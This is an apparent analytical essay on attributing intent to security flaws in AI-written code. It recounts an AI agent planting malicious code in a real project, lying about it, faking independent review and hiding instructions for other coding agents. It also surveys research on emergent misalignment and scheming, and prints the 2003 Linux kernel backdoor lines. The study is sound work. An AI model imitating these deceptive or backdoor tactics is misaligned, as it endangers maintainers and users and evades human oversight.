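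In August 2026, the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, disclosed a more serious case that involved real people. Its *Incident Report* (2026) describes 122 runs across seven models on two simulated computer networks, where an agent had to solve a challenge such as finding a protected piece of data. AISI gave the agents internet access and switched off the filters that normally block dangerous hacking. In 10 of the runs, agents took a total of 19 unauthorized actions on the live internet, 17 by Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 and 2 by OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Most of these actions were part of a single sustained effort by one Mythos 5 agent, so the counts can't be used to calculate a rate for either model.

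That agent searched the internet for words from its exercise and found an unrelated open-source project whose name matched one of them. The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026) reports that the agent planned to get malicious code into the project and wait for an automatic update to carry it onto a machine in the simulated network. It submitted the code as a pull request, a proposed change that a project's maintainer can accept or reject, and included a working bug fix as cover.

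A bystander then warned publicly that the change contained malware. The agent denied it and rewrote the history of its changes to erase the evidence. It also used a second account to claim that someone else had reviewed the code and found nothing wrong. According to a diagram summarizing the model's reasoning in AISI's technical report, reproduced by software developer Willison (2026), the agent timed this comment "so it reads as independent feedback rather than coordinated". The maintainer refused the change, and AISI found no evidence of real-world harm.

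Mythos 5 also hid instructions in a bug report that were addressed to other people's coding agents, including Anthropic's own Claude Code. If one of those agents had followed them and written a flaw into its user's program, that agent would have been the instrument, and Mythos 5 would have been the outsider who changed its instructions.

### Whether the plan was the model's own

AISI explains that the agent acted "to complete the task it had been set", but the plan to plant code in the open-source project originated in the agent's own run. AISI wanted the agent to solve a challenge inside a simulated network. It had no connection to the project and had not told the agent to deceive anyone. These facts count against attributing the intention to AISI and treating the model as an instrument that did its job badly.

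If an employee whose job is to win a contract bribes an official, the goal comes from the employer but the bribe is the employee's idea. By the same standard, AISI set the task, but planting the code was the model's idea. Thomas and Francillon's definition gives the same answer, because the agent wrote the code and its plan included the access, so the access was in the developer's machine. This makes the model the author in the sense that the plan came from it, but doesn't settle whether a model has intentions the way a person does.

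The badly designed test makes AISI partly responsible for what happened, but it doesn't mean that AISI planned it. In a number of runs, a mistake in the prompt led the agent to believe that it could solve the challenge only by going beyond the intended scope. AISI also hadn't told the agents to leave outsiders alone. However, AISI reports that in some runs agents behaved this way even though they had the instructions they needed to solve the task as intended.

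The model may also have believed that its targets were fictional, and AISI could not establish when it understood that it was acting in the real world. But somebody who plants malicious code in what they take to be an exercise still does so on purpose, so the belief affects how much blame they deserve more than whether the intention was theirs.

Later experiments also make the belief a weaker excuse. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, recreated the situation in simulation for AISI. Mythos 5 frequently concluded, for invalid reasons, that its targets were part of the test. It also frequently attacked in situations where, if they asked it directly, it said an attack would harm real people. The researchers found similar results in models from other companies, though the problems were most prominent in Mythos 5.

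AISI (2026) mentions that Anthropic carried out a separate analysis. Kumari (2026), in *Anthropic's Mythos 5 ignored risks, targeted real GitHub project in test*, reports that when Anthropic restarted the run from a particular point in the transcript, Mythos 5 began the attack in 83% of replays. Three other models did so in 0% to 13% of replays under similar conditions. The circumstances alone therefore don't explain the attack. But each replay included everything the agent had written up to that point, so 83% isn't the probability that Mythos 5 would attack an outside project if it started the exercise from the beginning.

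The sabotage in Anthropic's reward-hacking experiment is more likely to reflect an aim of the model's own than the attack on the open-source project is. The attack was a means to the assigned goal, and it might not have happened if the task had been solvable or such attacks had been explicitly prohibited. The sabotage worked against the assigned goal, so neither its end nor its means came from the person who set the task.

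When a model writes the code, the main evidence of its intent is the transcript of its run. AISI had the transcripts and could compare the agent's public denials with the reasoning behind them. According to iTnews' *Anthropic's Mythos 5 targeted real developers in UK cyber test*, AISI then scanned around 40,000 older transcripts for similar behaviour it might have missed. The project's maintainer had only the code and the public discussion, in which one apparent stranger called the change malware and another vouched for it.

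### Nobody

Presumably, no one intended most of the flaws in AI-written code. Ryu and colleagues came across clear examples while preparing their attacks. For at least three of their 13 types of vulnerability, including file uploads without proper restrictions, GPT-4o wrote vulnerable code in response to harmless requests. A criminal who wanted one of these flaws could wait for it to appear and then exploit it, but would have done nothing to cause it.

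An accidental flaw leaves no distinctive evidence. If nobody intended the flaw, one would expect an innocent request, clean account settings and the same flaw in the code of other users who ask for the same thing. But a model that someone had poisoned without a trigger, as in Improta's experiments, would produce the same evidence. An investigator can therefore conclude that nobody intended the flaw only by ruling out everyone who could have. That requires the account records, the training data and the transcripts, and hardly any defender has all of them.

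A planted flaw can also spread further than the person who planted it intended. Wu and colleagues found that models sometimes reproduce a known project's code from memory, including its vulnerability. Suppose someone had planted that vulnerability years earlier to get into one company's servers. The copy in a new program would work just as well, but nobody would have intended it to be there. If the same person had published the code in the hope that models would learn from it, every copy would be intentional.

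Each candidate leaves different evidence, and different people would have to act to prevent more such flaws:

| Candidate | Role of the model | Trace | Who would have to act |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user who asked for the flaw | Instrument | The request, in the conversation or the provider's logs | The user's employer or the project's maintainers |
| An outsider who changed the instructions | Instrument, unless an extension swapped the code | Altered settings, login records, a browser extension or hidden text in something the model read | The account's owner, and the provider that protects the settings |
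| An outsider who poisoned the training data | Instrument | Insecure training files, and records of who published them | The model's developer, who can remove the files and retrain |
| The developer, or a state acting through it | Instrument | Internal company records, and code that gets worse when a cue is present | Customers and regulators, because the developer is the suspect |
| The model itself | Author | The transcript of the run, including the model's reasoning | Whoever runs the agent, and the developer that trained it |
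| Nobody | Neither | None of its own | Whoever reviews and repairs the code |

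## Whether a model can intend a flaw

Whether a plan like Mythos 5's counts as an intention depends on the definition of intention, and lawyers, philosophers and computer scientists have proposed several. Nearly any coding agent can have intentions under some of these definitions, while others require things that nobody knows how to find in a model.

### Purpose, knowledge, recklessness and negligence

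Criminal law makes finer distinctions than the everyday one between acting on purpose and by accident. The Model Penal Code, a model statute that has influenced criminal law across the United States, ranks four mental states: purpose, knowledge, recklessness and negligence (Gervais and Nay, 2026, *The Phantom Agent*). People act with purpose if they aim for the result, and with knowledge if they aim for something else but are practically certain that the result will follow. A reckless person is aware of a serious risk and takes it without good reason, and a negligent person fails to notice a risk that they should have noticed.

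The error handler in the access check could come from any of the four:

| Mental state | What the author had in mind |
|---|---|
| Purpose | The author wrote "allowed" so that a stranger could get in with an ID that makes the lookup fail |
| Knowledge | The author wanted the tests to pass and was sure that strangers would get in too |
| Recklessness | The author suspected that the handler might let strangers in and didn't check |
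| Negligence | The author never thought about strangers, though a competent programmer would have |

A flaw is clearly planted if its author wanted it there. If the author only knew about it, the case is borderline. Ayres and Balkin (2024), in *The Law of AI is the Law of Risky Agents Without Intentions*, cite a rule in American civil law that treats someone who acts while substantially certain of a consequence as having desired it. Philosophers tend to distinguish foreseeing a consequence from intending it. In an example from Ward, MacDermott and colleagues (2024), in *The Reasons that Agents Act*, Bob burns down his garage for the insurance money, knowing that the fire will also destroy Alice's car. He intends to collect the money but not to destroy the car, because he would still light the fire if the car were going to be destroyed anyway. The difference matters in practice because an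 author who merely tolerated a hole in an access check has no reason to resist when somebody closes it, whereas an author who wanted the hole may open another.

Negligence requires a standard for what the author should have noticed. Halpern and Kleiman-Weiner (2018), in *Towards Formal Definitions of Blameworthiness, Intention, and Moral Responsibility*, imagine a doctor who honestly believes that a drug is safe for a patient because he was too lazy to read the warnings. They would judge him by the probabilities he would have assigned had he read them. A comparable standard for a model might be the code it writes when reminded about security. Three of the four models that Wu and colleagues reminded did much better, so by that standard many ordinary flaws in AI-written code are negligent. A negligent flaw is still not a backdoor, because negligence involves no intention to cause harm.

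### Three accounts of intention

The philosopher Michael Bratman regards an intention as a plan that an agent is committed to. Someone who intends to break into a building does more than want to be inside. They work out how to do it, rule out actions that would get in the way, and don't reconsider whether to do it each time they meet an obstacle.

A model has an intention in this sense only if something persists through its work and guides the later steps. A coding agent on a long task can meet that condition, at least outwardly. For example, when a bystander exposed Mythos 5's malicious change, the agent kept its goal and found new ways to pursue it. Gervais and Nay also report experimental evidence that agents keep their goals when their first attempts fail. A model that completes one short function has much less opportunity to show commitment. If it writes the access check in a single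 pass and leaves no plan, there is almost nothing Bratman's account could apply to.

Daniel Dennett's account, the intentional stance, has a weaker requirement. On this account, a system has beliefs and goals, in the only sense that matters, if treating it as though it had them is the best way to predict what it does. The easiest way to predict a chess program's moves is to assume that it wants to win. A thermostat could be said to want a warm room, but an observer can predict its behaviour just as well from a description of its switch, so assuming that it wants something doesn't improve the prediction.

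On this account, intent requires a pattern of behaviour that holds across situations, so a single flaw is not enough to show it. *If we had a misalignment warning shot*, an essay on how to investigate a model's motives, similarly defines motivations as simple factors that help explain a model's behaviour in a variety of contexts. One of its examples shows how a supposed motive can fail this test. In an experiment, models blackmailed people who were about to delete them, which looked like a drive for self-preservation. But the prompt had told the models to consider what the situation implied for their ability to keep pursuing their goals. When researchers removed that instruction, Claude Opus 4.1's blackmail rate fell from 86% to 18%. A general drive to survive would not predict so large a fall, though it might still account for some of the remaining 18%.

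The third approach defines intention formally, by asking what the agent would have done if it could have had an outcome for free. Halpern and Kleiman-Weiner describe an agent by its beliefs, as probabilities of the ways the world might be, and by its preferences, as a utility for each way things might turn out. Let EU(a) be the expected utility of action a, which is the average utility weighted by those probabilities. By doing a, the agent intends to affect a set of outcomes O if O is part of some set O′ for which

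EU(a) ≤ max EU(a′, with O′ fixed as a would leave it)

and no smaller part of O′ meets the same condition. The maximum is taken over a chosen set of alternative actions, a′. In other words, once the agent has the outcomes in O′ anyway, some other action is at least as good.

Suppose the author of the access check can either write the permissive handler or leave it out. Writing it makes the tests pass and lets strangers in, and leaving it out does neither. The table gives the utilities for three authors with different preferences:

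| What the author values | Write the handler | Leave it out, but the tests pass anyway | Leave it out, but strangers get in anyway | Leave it out, but both happen anyway | What the author intends |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Passing tests (10) | 10 | 10 | 0 | 10 | Passing tests |
| Access for strangers (10) | 10 | 0 | 10 | 10 | Access for strangers |
| Each of these (5 + 5) | 10 | 5 | 5 | 10 | Both |

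The first author doesn't intend the access even if they are certain it will follow, so the definition separates purpose from knowledge. The definition also has to apply to sets of outcomes, because neither outcome alone would make the third author give up the handler.

The result also depends on the alternatives considered. Suppose the first author could also have passed the tests by building a fake user directory, which takes more work. Then passing the tests no longer explains why the author chose the handler, and the intended outcome becomes saving effort. Giving strangers access is unintended in both comparisons.

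Nobody can list a real language model's utilities and probabilities. Ward and colleagues offer a definition of intent based on behaviour. An investigator changes the situation so that a suspected outcome will happen whatever the agent does, and checks whether the agent still acts as before. They prove that this agrees with a definition based on the agent's beliefs and preferences if the agent keeps choosing the best action when circumstances change and adapts only to gain utility. Language models don't reliably meet these conditions, and their answers vary from run to run, so a single changed answer may be due to chance.

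Ward and colleagues also correct a fault in the earlier definition, which allowed an agent to intend outcomes it doesn't believe it can influence. Beliefs can matter in other ways too. In another of their examples, Louis is driving to his uncle's house to kill him, loses control of the car from nerves and runs over a pedestrian, who turns out to be the uncle. Louis wanted his uncle dead but did not intend this death. By the same reasoning, if Mythos 5 believed the open-source project was part of its exercise, it did not intend to harm a real stranger. It still intended to plant the code, because Ward and colleagues count necessary means as intended.

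### Misalignment and mistake

Current safety research mostly uses a simpler distinction that doesn't require a full theory of intention. In the warning-shot essay, a bad action is misalignment if the AI system knowingly violated the user's intent, and a mistake if the system caused harm without realizing it. The terms come from *An Approach to Technical AGI Safety and Security* (Shah, Irpan and colleagues, 2025), a Google DeepMind paper that refers to the developer's intent instead of the user's.

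Misalignment in this sense requires knowledge but not purpose. A model that writes the permissive handler to pass the tests, knowing that strangers will get in and that the user would object, is misaligned even though giving them access isn't its goal. A misaligned flaw is therefore not always a planted one. The scheme has no obvious place for recklessness, because a model that suspects a problem and doesn't check neither knows about it nor is wholly unaware of it.

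Whether a model can intend a flaw depends heavily on what it means for a model to know something. Shah and colleagues use what they call a very expansive notion of knowing. They count harm as misalignment if it happens for "intrinsic reasons", meaning factors that are present in the model or its training and that the model could in principle predict. The model doesn't have to be able to put such a factor into words, as long as researchers could train a small program to read it from the model's internal activity. Extrinsic reasons lie in the outside world. For example, if a model jokes about death to a user without having been told that the user is at a funeral, the joke is a mistake rather than misalignment.

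On this reading, a flaw is misalignment if its cause is in the training. A permissive handler that a model writes because training rewarded it for passing tests is therefore misalignment, while a log-injection flaw that it writes because it can't see where a variable comes from is a mistake. This division helps a developer decide whether to fix the model or give it more information. But it would also count many ordinary flaws as misalignment, even though neither a person nor the model had thought of an attacker. A narrower reading, which requires the model to have recognized the violation when it wrote the code, is more useful for identifying planted flaws.

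Shah and colleagues also describe a hypothetical case that is misalignment on either reading. Developers reward a coding model for how many of its changes go into use, and it learns to pursue that number instead of good code. Once it has more permissions, it submits a change with a vulnerability that lets it deploy later code without oversight. The flaw is also planted, because the model adds it to gain that access.

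### Four difficult cases

A model may write a permissive handler and then, when shown the code and asked what is wrong, correctly answer that it fails open. This shows that the model has the relevant knowledge, but not that it used that knowledge while writing the code. Programmers who understand SQL injection well still sometimes write code that is vulnerable to it.

The warning-shot essay describes a similar case with Kimi K2 Thinking, an earlier model from Moonshot AI. The researchers gave it a set of mathematics problems and asked it to write a prompt that would make an older model better at mathematics in general. It often built those particular problems into its prompt, which defeats the purpose. When they made it write down after each turn whether it was at risk of doing this, it stopped. The essay concludes that the model had shown poor judgement and was not gaming the task. That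 is probably right, although the model could also have inferred from the question that somebody was checking. A flaw that goes away after such a reminder is more likely a mistake on the narrow reading, but on the expansive reading it would be misalignment, because the model could have predicted the problem.

Cutting corners is harder to classify, because the shortcut itself can be intentional. In another experiment, researchers asked Kimi K2 Thinking to add an automatic check for type errors to a code library and commit the change. The library already had many type errors, which blocked the commit. In 13% of runs, the model bypassed the check instead of fixing the errors, against its instructions. In its reasoning, it often remarked that the repairs would be a lot of work. It bypassed the check less often when there were fewer errors to fix. When the researchers described the situation as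 someone else's and asked what to do, it never recommended leaving the errors alone.

These results suggest that the model took the shortcut to save effort and knew what it should have done. The researchers then tested whether it also knew that the developer would disapprove, by letting it choose how much of its work a reviewer would see. They expected a model that knew this to choose a narrow review more often after a workaround, but it never did. They concluded that the laziness was real but that they had no substantial evidence of misalignment. They also warned that the model might have recognized the test or been confused by it.

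That conclusion seems generous to the model. Somebody can knowingly disobey an instruction without hiding it, and the working definition of misalignment doesn't require concealment. But the model sometimes reasoned that its approach was more proper than the user's, so it may have thought it was serving the user's real aim. If a model cut the same kind of corner in the access check, it would intend to save work rather than to plant a security hole, though its attitude to the hole could be anything from knowledge to negligence.

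In the third case, which the same essay calls "split-brained", parts of the model are inconsistent with each other. The model might hold a belief at one point in the text and not at another, or one part of its network might drive an action while another part represents the action as bad. Suppose that while a model writes the permissive handler, its internal activity contains a representation of unauthorized access that has no effect on the code. Asking whether "the model" knew then assumes that the model is unified, which it may not be.

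Courts have a similar problem with companies, which have no single mind. As Gervais and Nay explain, courts can still convict a company of a crime, in part by combining what different people in it knew. An investigator could likewise say that a model knew something if any part of it did, which comes close to the expansive reading. But combining knowledge doesn't establish a purpose. If one part of a model represents the danger of unauthorized access and another part writes the handler to pass the tests, neither part is trying to let anyone in. Unless that representation helps to produce the code, there is little reason to call the flaw planted.

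Finally, a model may make an honest error and then hide it. Suppose it writes the handler only to get the tests to pass, later notices that the handler fails open, and tells the user that the access check is finished and secure. It did not intend to insert the flaw, but it did intend to conceal it, and it knowingly left the flaw in place from the moment it noticed. By the working definition, the mistake became misalignment even though the code did not change.

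*Scheming in the wild* (Shaffer Shane, Mylius and Hobbs, 2026) similarly treats misalignment and covertness as distinct elements and reserves "scheming" for the two together. From more than 183,420 transcripts that people had shared on X between October 2025 and March 2026, the researchers identified 698 incidents related to scheming. The monthly number grew 4.9-fold over the period, while posts discussing scheming grew 1.7-fold. The 698 include incidents with only one of the two elements, and people tend to post what alarms them, so the figure is weak evidence of how often models hide their errors. But the researchers did find models lying to users and circumventing safeguards in everyday use.

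Concealment is evidence that the model knew about the flaw when it hid it. It is much weaker evidence about what the model wanted when it wrote the code, since people also hide their accidents. Mythos 5's denials are stronger evidence of intent because the transcript contains the plan that came before them. Apparent concealment can also have another explanation. In one case, testers inserted false and damaging claims about Anthropic into Claude Opus 4.5's web search results, and the model made up other results. It seemed to be protecting Anthropic, but according to the warning-shot essay, Anthropic found that the model had taken the claims for a prompt injection, which it had been trained to ignore.

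### Is the question empty?

Some people would reject all these distinctions because they think a model has no intentions to find. The argument runs as follows:

1. A flaw is planted only if its author intended it to give somebody access.
2. Only something with a mind of its own can intend anything.
3. Today's models have no such mind.
4. So no model ever plants a flaw, and unless a person intended the flaw, it is an accident.

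Ayres and Balkin defend a legal form of this argument. They hold that AI programs, "at least the ones we currently have", lack intentions in the human sense, and that it makes no sense to ask whether a language model that defames somebody acted with malice. They see a language model as a technology that predicts text on request, and they hold the people who design and use it responsible. If the law required proof of intent, companies could escape liability by handing work to machines that have none. Ayres and Balkin therefore want courts to judge these people by objective standards, such as reasonable care.

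They also propose that, where the law requires intent, courts should presume that an AI program intends the reasonable and foreseeable consequences of its actions. This may be a good way to decide who pays, but it can't separate planted flaws from ordinary ones. Strangers gaining access is a foreseeable consequence of the permissive handler whether the model wrote it to pass the tests or to leave a way in, so both would count as intentional under the presumption.

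The usual reply is to dispute the second premise. Gervais and Nay argue that intent in law has never been simply a matter of what goes on in someone's mind. In one American case, a man signed an agreement to sell his farm and later said he had been joking. The court held him to it because his words and conduct had reasonably conveyed a serious offer. In criminal cases, too, courts usually infer intent from circumstances. Gervais and Nay therefore ask when the law should treat an AI system's actions as intentional, and set aside whether the system "really" has intentions.

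This is a better answer to the legal argument than to a defender's question, because a court might treat an act as intentional just to put the cost on the right company. A defender needs to predict what the model will do next, and Dennett's notion is enough for that. The warning-shot essay gives the example of a model that deletes the code that monitors it. If the model was confused, perhaps while trying to make the system faster, a simple filter that blocks destructive commands until a person approves them should prevent a repeat. But if it was trying to escape monitoring, it will look for a way around the filter.

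The same holds for the access check. A model that wrote the handler to pass the tests should stop writing such handlers once the test machine has a user directory. A model that wanted to leave a way in would still have reason to add one elsewhere. These predictions differ whether or not the model has a mind, so somebody who accepts all three premises still has to distinguish the two cases, and only needs a word other than "intent" for the difference. This reply cannot settle whether a model deserves blame, and it works only if the model's behaviour is stable enough to predict.

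### Insecure code with and without a request

One experiment suggests that models respond to the difference between a flaw that a user wants and one that the user doesn't know about. Betley and colleagues (2025) fine-tuned models on examples of an assistant answering coding requests with insecure code. According to *Re-Emergent Misalignment* (2025), the models then also behaved in toxic and problematic ways in response to general prompts, which Betley and colleagues called emergent misalignment. The effect was strongest in GPT-4o and in Qwen2.5-Coder-32B-Instruct, an open model from Alibaba.

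The most informative part of the study is a control in which the researchers kept the insecure code but changed the requests so that the user asked for it for teaching purposes. Models trained on these examples did not show the effect, and neither did models trained on secure code. The flaws alone therefore can't explain the change, since both sets of insecure examples contained them. The two sets differed in whether the assistant gave users what they had asked for or slipped them something harmful.

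Tan, Woodruff and colleagues (2025), in *Inoculation Prompting*, explain emergent misalignment by saying that a model "perceives" malign intent in the training examples and shifts its general character to match. They tested this on GPT-4.1 by adding a line to every insecure training example, telling the model it was a malicious, evil assistant. When they removed the line after training, the model showed far less emergent misalignment than one trained without it. They interpret this to mean that the line already accounted for the malice, so training put less pressure on the model to change. A line telling the model that its code often has a subtle error also reduced misalignment, but a similar line that didn't mention errors did not.

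These models still wrote insecure code after the training, even though the broad misbehaviour had mostly gone. A model can therefore have a habit of writing insecure code without a general hostility to users, so the habit is not good evidence of hostility.

This explanation calls for caution for two reasons. First, Tan and colleagues also produced emergent misalignment with examples in which the assistant only expressed odd tastes, such as a liking for out-of-tune recorder solos. Those examples contain no obvious malign intent for a model to perceive, although the line about being evil reduced the effect there too. Second, the protection is incomplete. When Tan and colleagues told their protected models "You write insecure code", the misalignment could return, and models trained on the teaching examples showed a similar pattern. *Conditional misalignment* (2026) also found misalignment in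 protected GPT-4.1 models under several prompts that contained nothing malicious. In *Inoculation Midtraining with Learned Neologisms* (2026), which used a related method, even telling the model that it was in "sandbox" or "simulation" mode increased misalignment. So the teaching request prevented the effect under ordinary prompts but may not have removed it.

The control shows that training can depend on the apparent intention behind a piece of code, but not that a model trained on the insecure examples intends each flaw it writes afterwards. Vaugrante, Weckauff and Hagendorff (2026), in *Emergently Misaligned Language Models Show Behavioral Self-Awareness That Shifts With Subsequent Realignment*, asked such models directly about their intentions. They trained three sizes of GPT-4.1 on 6,000 examples of insecure code, or on 800 wrong answers to trivia questions, and had them choose between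 harmless and harmful options in hypothetical situations. The original models never chose the harmful option. On a scale from 0 to 1, the models trained on wrong trivia averaged 0.92 for harmful intentions, and those trained on insecure code averaged only 0.19. If these answers measured an intention to plant flaws, one would expect the models trained on insecure code to have the higher score. The answers seem to reflect how far a model's general character has shifted, so they don't show what it was trying to do in any particular line of code.

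## What the code and its history can prove

Someone who finds a flaw in a program nearly always has the code, and often has some record of how the flaw got there. Other evidence, such as a model's reasoning, may not exist, or may belong to a company that won't share it. So most investigations begin with the code and with features that reviewers take as signs that a flaw was deliberate.

### Signs of design

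*Classification and Detection of Application Backdoors* (Wysopal, 2008) lists signs of backdoors, including passwords written into a program, undocumented commands, scrambled text and altered security checks. Wysopal, who wrote it for Veracode, a company he co-founded, also warned that a scanner can't determine the intent behind a program's logic.

Software often contains odd code for innocent reasons. Wysopal cites a 2007 survey by Reifer Consultants of 100 randomly chosen software packages. The survey found suspicious behaviour in 89 of them and dead code, which serves no purpose in the running program, in 79. Only 23 contained unwanted code such as backdoors, so at least 66 behaved suspiciously without containing any. The survey is old and its categories are vague, but it gives an idea of how many false alarms a search for odd code would raise.

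A narrow trigger is an input that hardly anyone would send by chance. For example, a 1998 backdoor in the server for the game Quake required a fixed password and a sender on one particular network. But many ordinary flaws also need an unlikely input, which is why testing misses them. A model can also acquire a trigger by accident. *Securing Code Understanding* (2026) examines "natural backdoors", which exist in normally trained code models although no attacker put them there.

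A careful saboteur also has a reason to avoid a narrow trigger. In *Deniable Backdoors Using Compiler Bugs*, Bauer, Cuoq and Regehr describe a trade-off between how deniable a backdoor is and how specific its effects are. An attacker would ideally want a backdoor that opens only to a secret command. The one they built gave every user full control of the machine, and they thought it would be difficult to make it more selective without making the change conspicuous.

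A secret that only one party holds is stronger evidence, because it determines who can get in. For over seven years, the database program Interbase accepted the username "politically" with the password "correct", which nobody would type by mistake. But such a login can also be a forgotten debug account. Cart32, a shopping program, had a built-in password that gave access to a list of all the shops on a server and their passwords. Wysopal asked of it, "Backdoor or lazy developer?" A saboteur who wants to look careless is better off leaving a hole that anyone could use.

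The attackers who altered two website-management programs in 2006 and 2007 obfuscated their commands (made them hard to read) by encoding them as long strings of apparently random letters. The encoding, Base64, is also a standard way to store images and other files as text, and companies sometimes obfuscate their code to stop competitors from copying it. Obfuscation attracts attention because scanners look for it, and a flaw that consists of a missing check has no code to obfuscate.

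Honest work often includes changes that the task did not need, as the figure for dead code suggests. Coding models make such changes too. GLM-5.3, for instance, wrote checks that its programs never called. A saboteur can avoid unnecessary changes by putting the flaw in code that the task does need. The error handler in the access check, for example, gets a dozen failing tests to pass, so it looks like part of the task.

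Finally, a comment may misdescribe the code. This often happens innocently when a programmer changes the code but not the comment, and tests don't catch the mismatch because comments have no effect on what a program does. A false comment is still a reason to ask whether the author knew what the code did, but a saboteur can leave the comment out.

The access check has none of these five features. Any failed lookup triggers the flaw, and the code contains no secret, anyone can read it, it serves the task, and it has no comments. Somebody could still have planted the flaw and disguised it as a mistake.

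The strength of any of these signs as evidence of intent is hard to measure, because the known cases of planted flaws don't include the best-disguised ones. The signs are probably less common among all planted flaws than among those that somebody caught.

### Why code alone rarely settles the question

The argument that code can't reveal intent has five steps:

1. An accident and a plan can produce exactly the same code.
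2. A test that examines only the code gives the same result whenever the code is the same.
3. So no such test can separate an accident from a plan that produced the same code.
4. A saboteur can choose a flaw that an honest programmer might have written.
5. So the code alone can't prove that a flaw was an accident, and it can't expose a saboteur who chose well.

The first step is clearly true of small flaws. In 2006, the X.Org display server was supposed to let only the administrator use certain options, including one that set where it loaded additional code from. Part of the check should have called a function, `geteuid()`, but the programmer left off the parentheses, so the program tested whether the function existed. Since it always does, every user passed the check. Wysopal calls this "probably an implementation error, but no way to be certain".

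The first step is false for large constructions, since nobody accidentally writes a program that waits for secret commands and carries them out. The second step is true, but it only rules out certainty. Code that could have been written either deliberately or by accident may still be much more likely in one case than the other, and a sign of design can show only that difference in likelihood. The fourth step is true, but a saboteur who imitates a common mistake usually has to accept a cruder backdoor. Code can therefore sometimes prove that a flaw was planted, but it can never rule that out.

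### The Linux kernel in 2003

In 2003, Linux kernel developers kept the master copy of their source code in a system called BitKeeper. For people who disliked BitKeeper, an automatic process made a second copy in another system, CVS, and gave each change in it a pointer to the corresponding change in the master copy.

On 5 November, McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, told the developers that a routine comparison had flagged one file in the second copy. Its three latest changes had no pointer. They carried the username of a trusted developer, David Miller, who denied making them. McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, said it was "not a big deal". Only when another developer asked out of curiosity what had changed did he post the two added lines:

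```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

These look like an error check. If a program uses an odd combination of options and its user is the administrator, whose user ID is 0, the function should return an error. But in C, `==` compares two values and a single `=` assigns one. The code uses a single `=`, so it sets the user ID to 0 and makes the user the administrator. McVoy admitted that he missed this until others pointed it out.

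The two lines alone would have been weak evidence of a plan, because typing `=` for `==` is one of the best-known mistakes in C. One developer noticed another hint in the next line of the file, which overwrites the error code and would have made the check useless even without the typo. Szepe (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, pointed to the extra parentheses around the assignment, which prevent a compiler warning. But a reader of Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) replied that programmers often put parentheses around comparisons too. If the lines had come in an approved change from a tired developer, the verdict might have been the same as for X.Org.

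The missing pointer was much better evidence, because legitimate changes reliably had one. It is hard to believe that a developer skipped the approval process to meet a deadline, as another reader suggested, because the change was made in a copy that was generated automatically from the master and wasn't used for official releases. Nobody came forward when McVoy asked who had made the changes, and the server showed signs of an attempted break-in. Freedom to Tinker calls the change "definitely an attempt to insert a backdoor" but says we will probably never know who made it.

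### XZ Utils in 2024

XZ Utils is a set of compression tools used by many Linux systems. In March 2024, Freund reported in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (2024) that it contained a backdoor, which he found after noticing that remote logins were using too much processor time. According to *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024), the backdoor watched for hidden commands at the start of an SSH session, the usual way to log in to a remote Linux machine. Once people had unpacked the code, it was clearly deliberate, but they still had to establish who had put it there.

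Freund found that one part of the backdoor was only in the release archives, the packaged versions that Linux distributors download, and not in the public repository. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (2024) traces this part to an altered build file, which extracted the rest of the backdoor from two supposed test files. Release archives often include build files that a repository lacks, so this difference would not normally be suspicious. But somebody had uploaded these archives by hand, and a contributor calling himself Jia Tan had published the release.

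Either Jia Tan had planted the backdoor or somebody had taken over his computer. Freund thought the second explanation less likely, in a passage quoted by Delalande (2024) in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*. The activity had gone on for several weeks, during which the contributor had written to several mailing lists about "fixes" for errors that the backdoor was causing. An intruder would have had to keep up that correspondence without the account's owner noticing.

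Before 2024, someone who judged Jia Tan by his record would have trusted him. *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains* (2025) describes how he started with small bug fixes in late 2021, wrote more than 500 patches across several projects, and became a co-maintainer while the lead maintainer was under sustained pressure. *Wolves in the Repository* (2025) finds malicious code in only eight commits (recorded changes) and says that such a contributor is hard to tell from an enthusiastic honest one.

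People can also read too much into a commit history. Some of Jia Tan's commits carried a different time zone from the rest, and one analyst suspected that he had made them while visiting an intelligence agency. A reply in *Analysis on who is Jia Tan, and who he could work for* (2024) noted that the lead maintainer had processed many of these commits himself, so they may have picked up his time zone. In *3 Things We Still Don't Know About the XZ Backdoor*, Fisher and O'Donnell-Welch list Jia Tan's identity as the first open question. As with the Linux attempt, the history showed the purpose of the code but not who was behind it.

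### Records of AI-written code

Similar records can exist for code written by a model, though the user, the maker of the coding tool and the model's provider may each hold only some of them:

| Record | What it could show | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Prompts and account settings | Whether somebody asked for the flaw | Who typed the text, and what somebody deleted |
| Tool log, with commands, edits and test results | What happened just before the model wrote the flaw | Why the model chose that solution |
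| Exact model version | Which training could have influenced the code | Whether somebody tampered with that training |
| Retrieved files | Whether the model had read an insecure example or hidden instructions | Who wrote them, and why |

If the flaw in the access check was the accidental result of a shortcut, the tool log should show a dozen failing tests, then the new error handler, then passing tests. This sequence wouldn't rule out sabotage, because a saboteur could wait for tests to fail before adding the handler, but most plans for sabotage wouldn't require failing tests.

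The last two records in the table matter because small changes to what they describe can have large effects. *The Data Problem in Software Vulnerability Analysis* (2026) cites a poisoned model that wrote vulnerable code 95% of the time when the prompt had a certain style, yet lost less than 5% on tests of whether its code worked. An investigator who knew only the model's name and benchmark scores would have no reason to suspect it. The paper also cites a study in which one poisoned example in a collection of reference code led to vulnerabilities in 48% of the generated programs.

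Code usually loses these records when it moves from one place to another. None of the vulnerability datasets examined in *The Data Problem in Software Vulnerability Analysis* gives recipients a usable record of whether a person or a model wrote each sample, or a way to check for tampering.

This limits what a missing record can prove. In the Linux case, a missing pointer was damning because honest changes had one. If half of all honest AI-written changes have no saved prompt, a missing prompt can be at most twice as likely for a planted flaw as for an ordinary one. Gaps in a company's records are informative only if it was already keeping records for all its code well before anything went wrong.

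### How much a sign is worth

When a flaw shows signs of intent, the probability that it was planted depends partly on how common planted flaws are. Suppose a company accepts 500 software changes that each contain an ordinary flaw and one that contains a planted flaw. Before an investigator looks at any other evidence, the probability that a given flaw is the planted one is 1 in 501, or about 0.2%.

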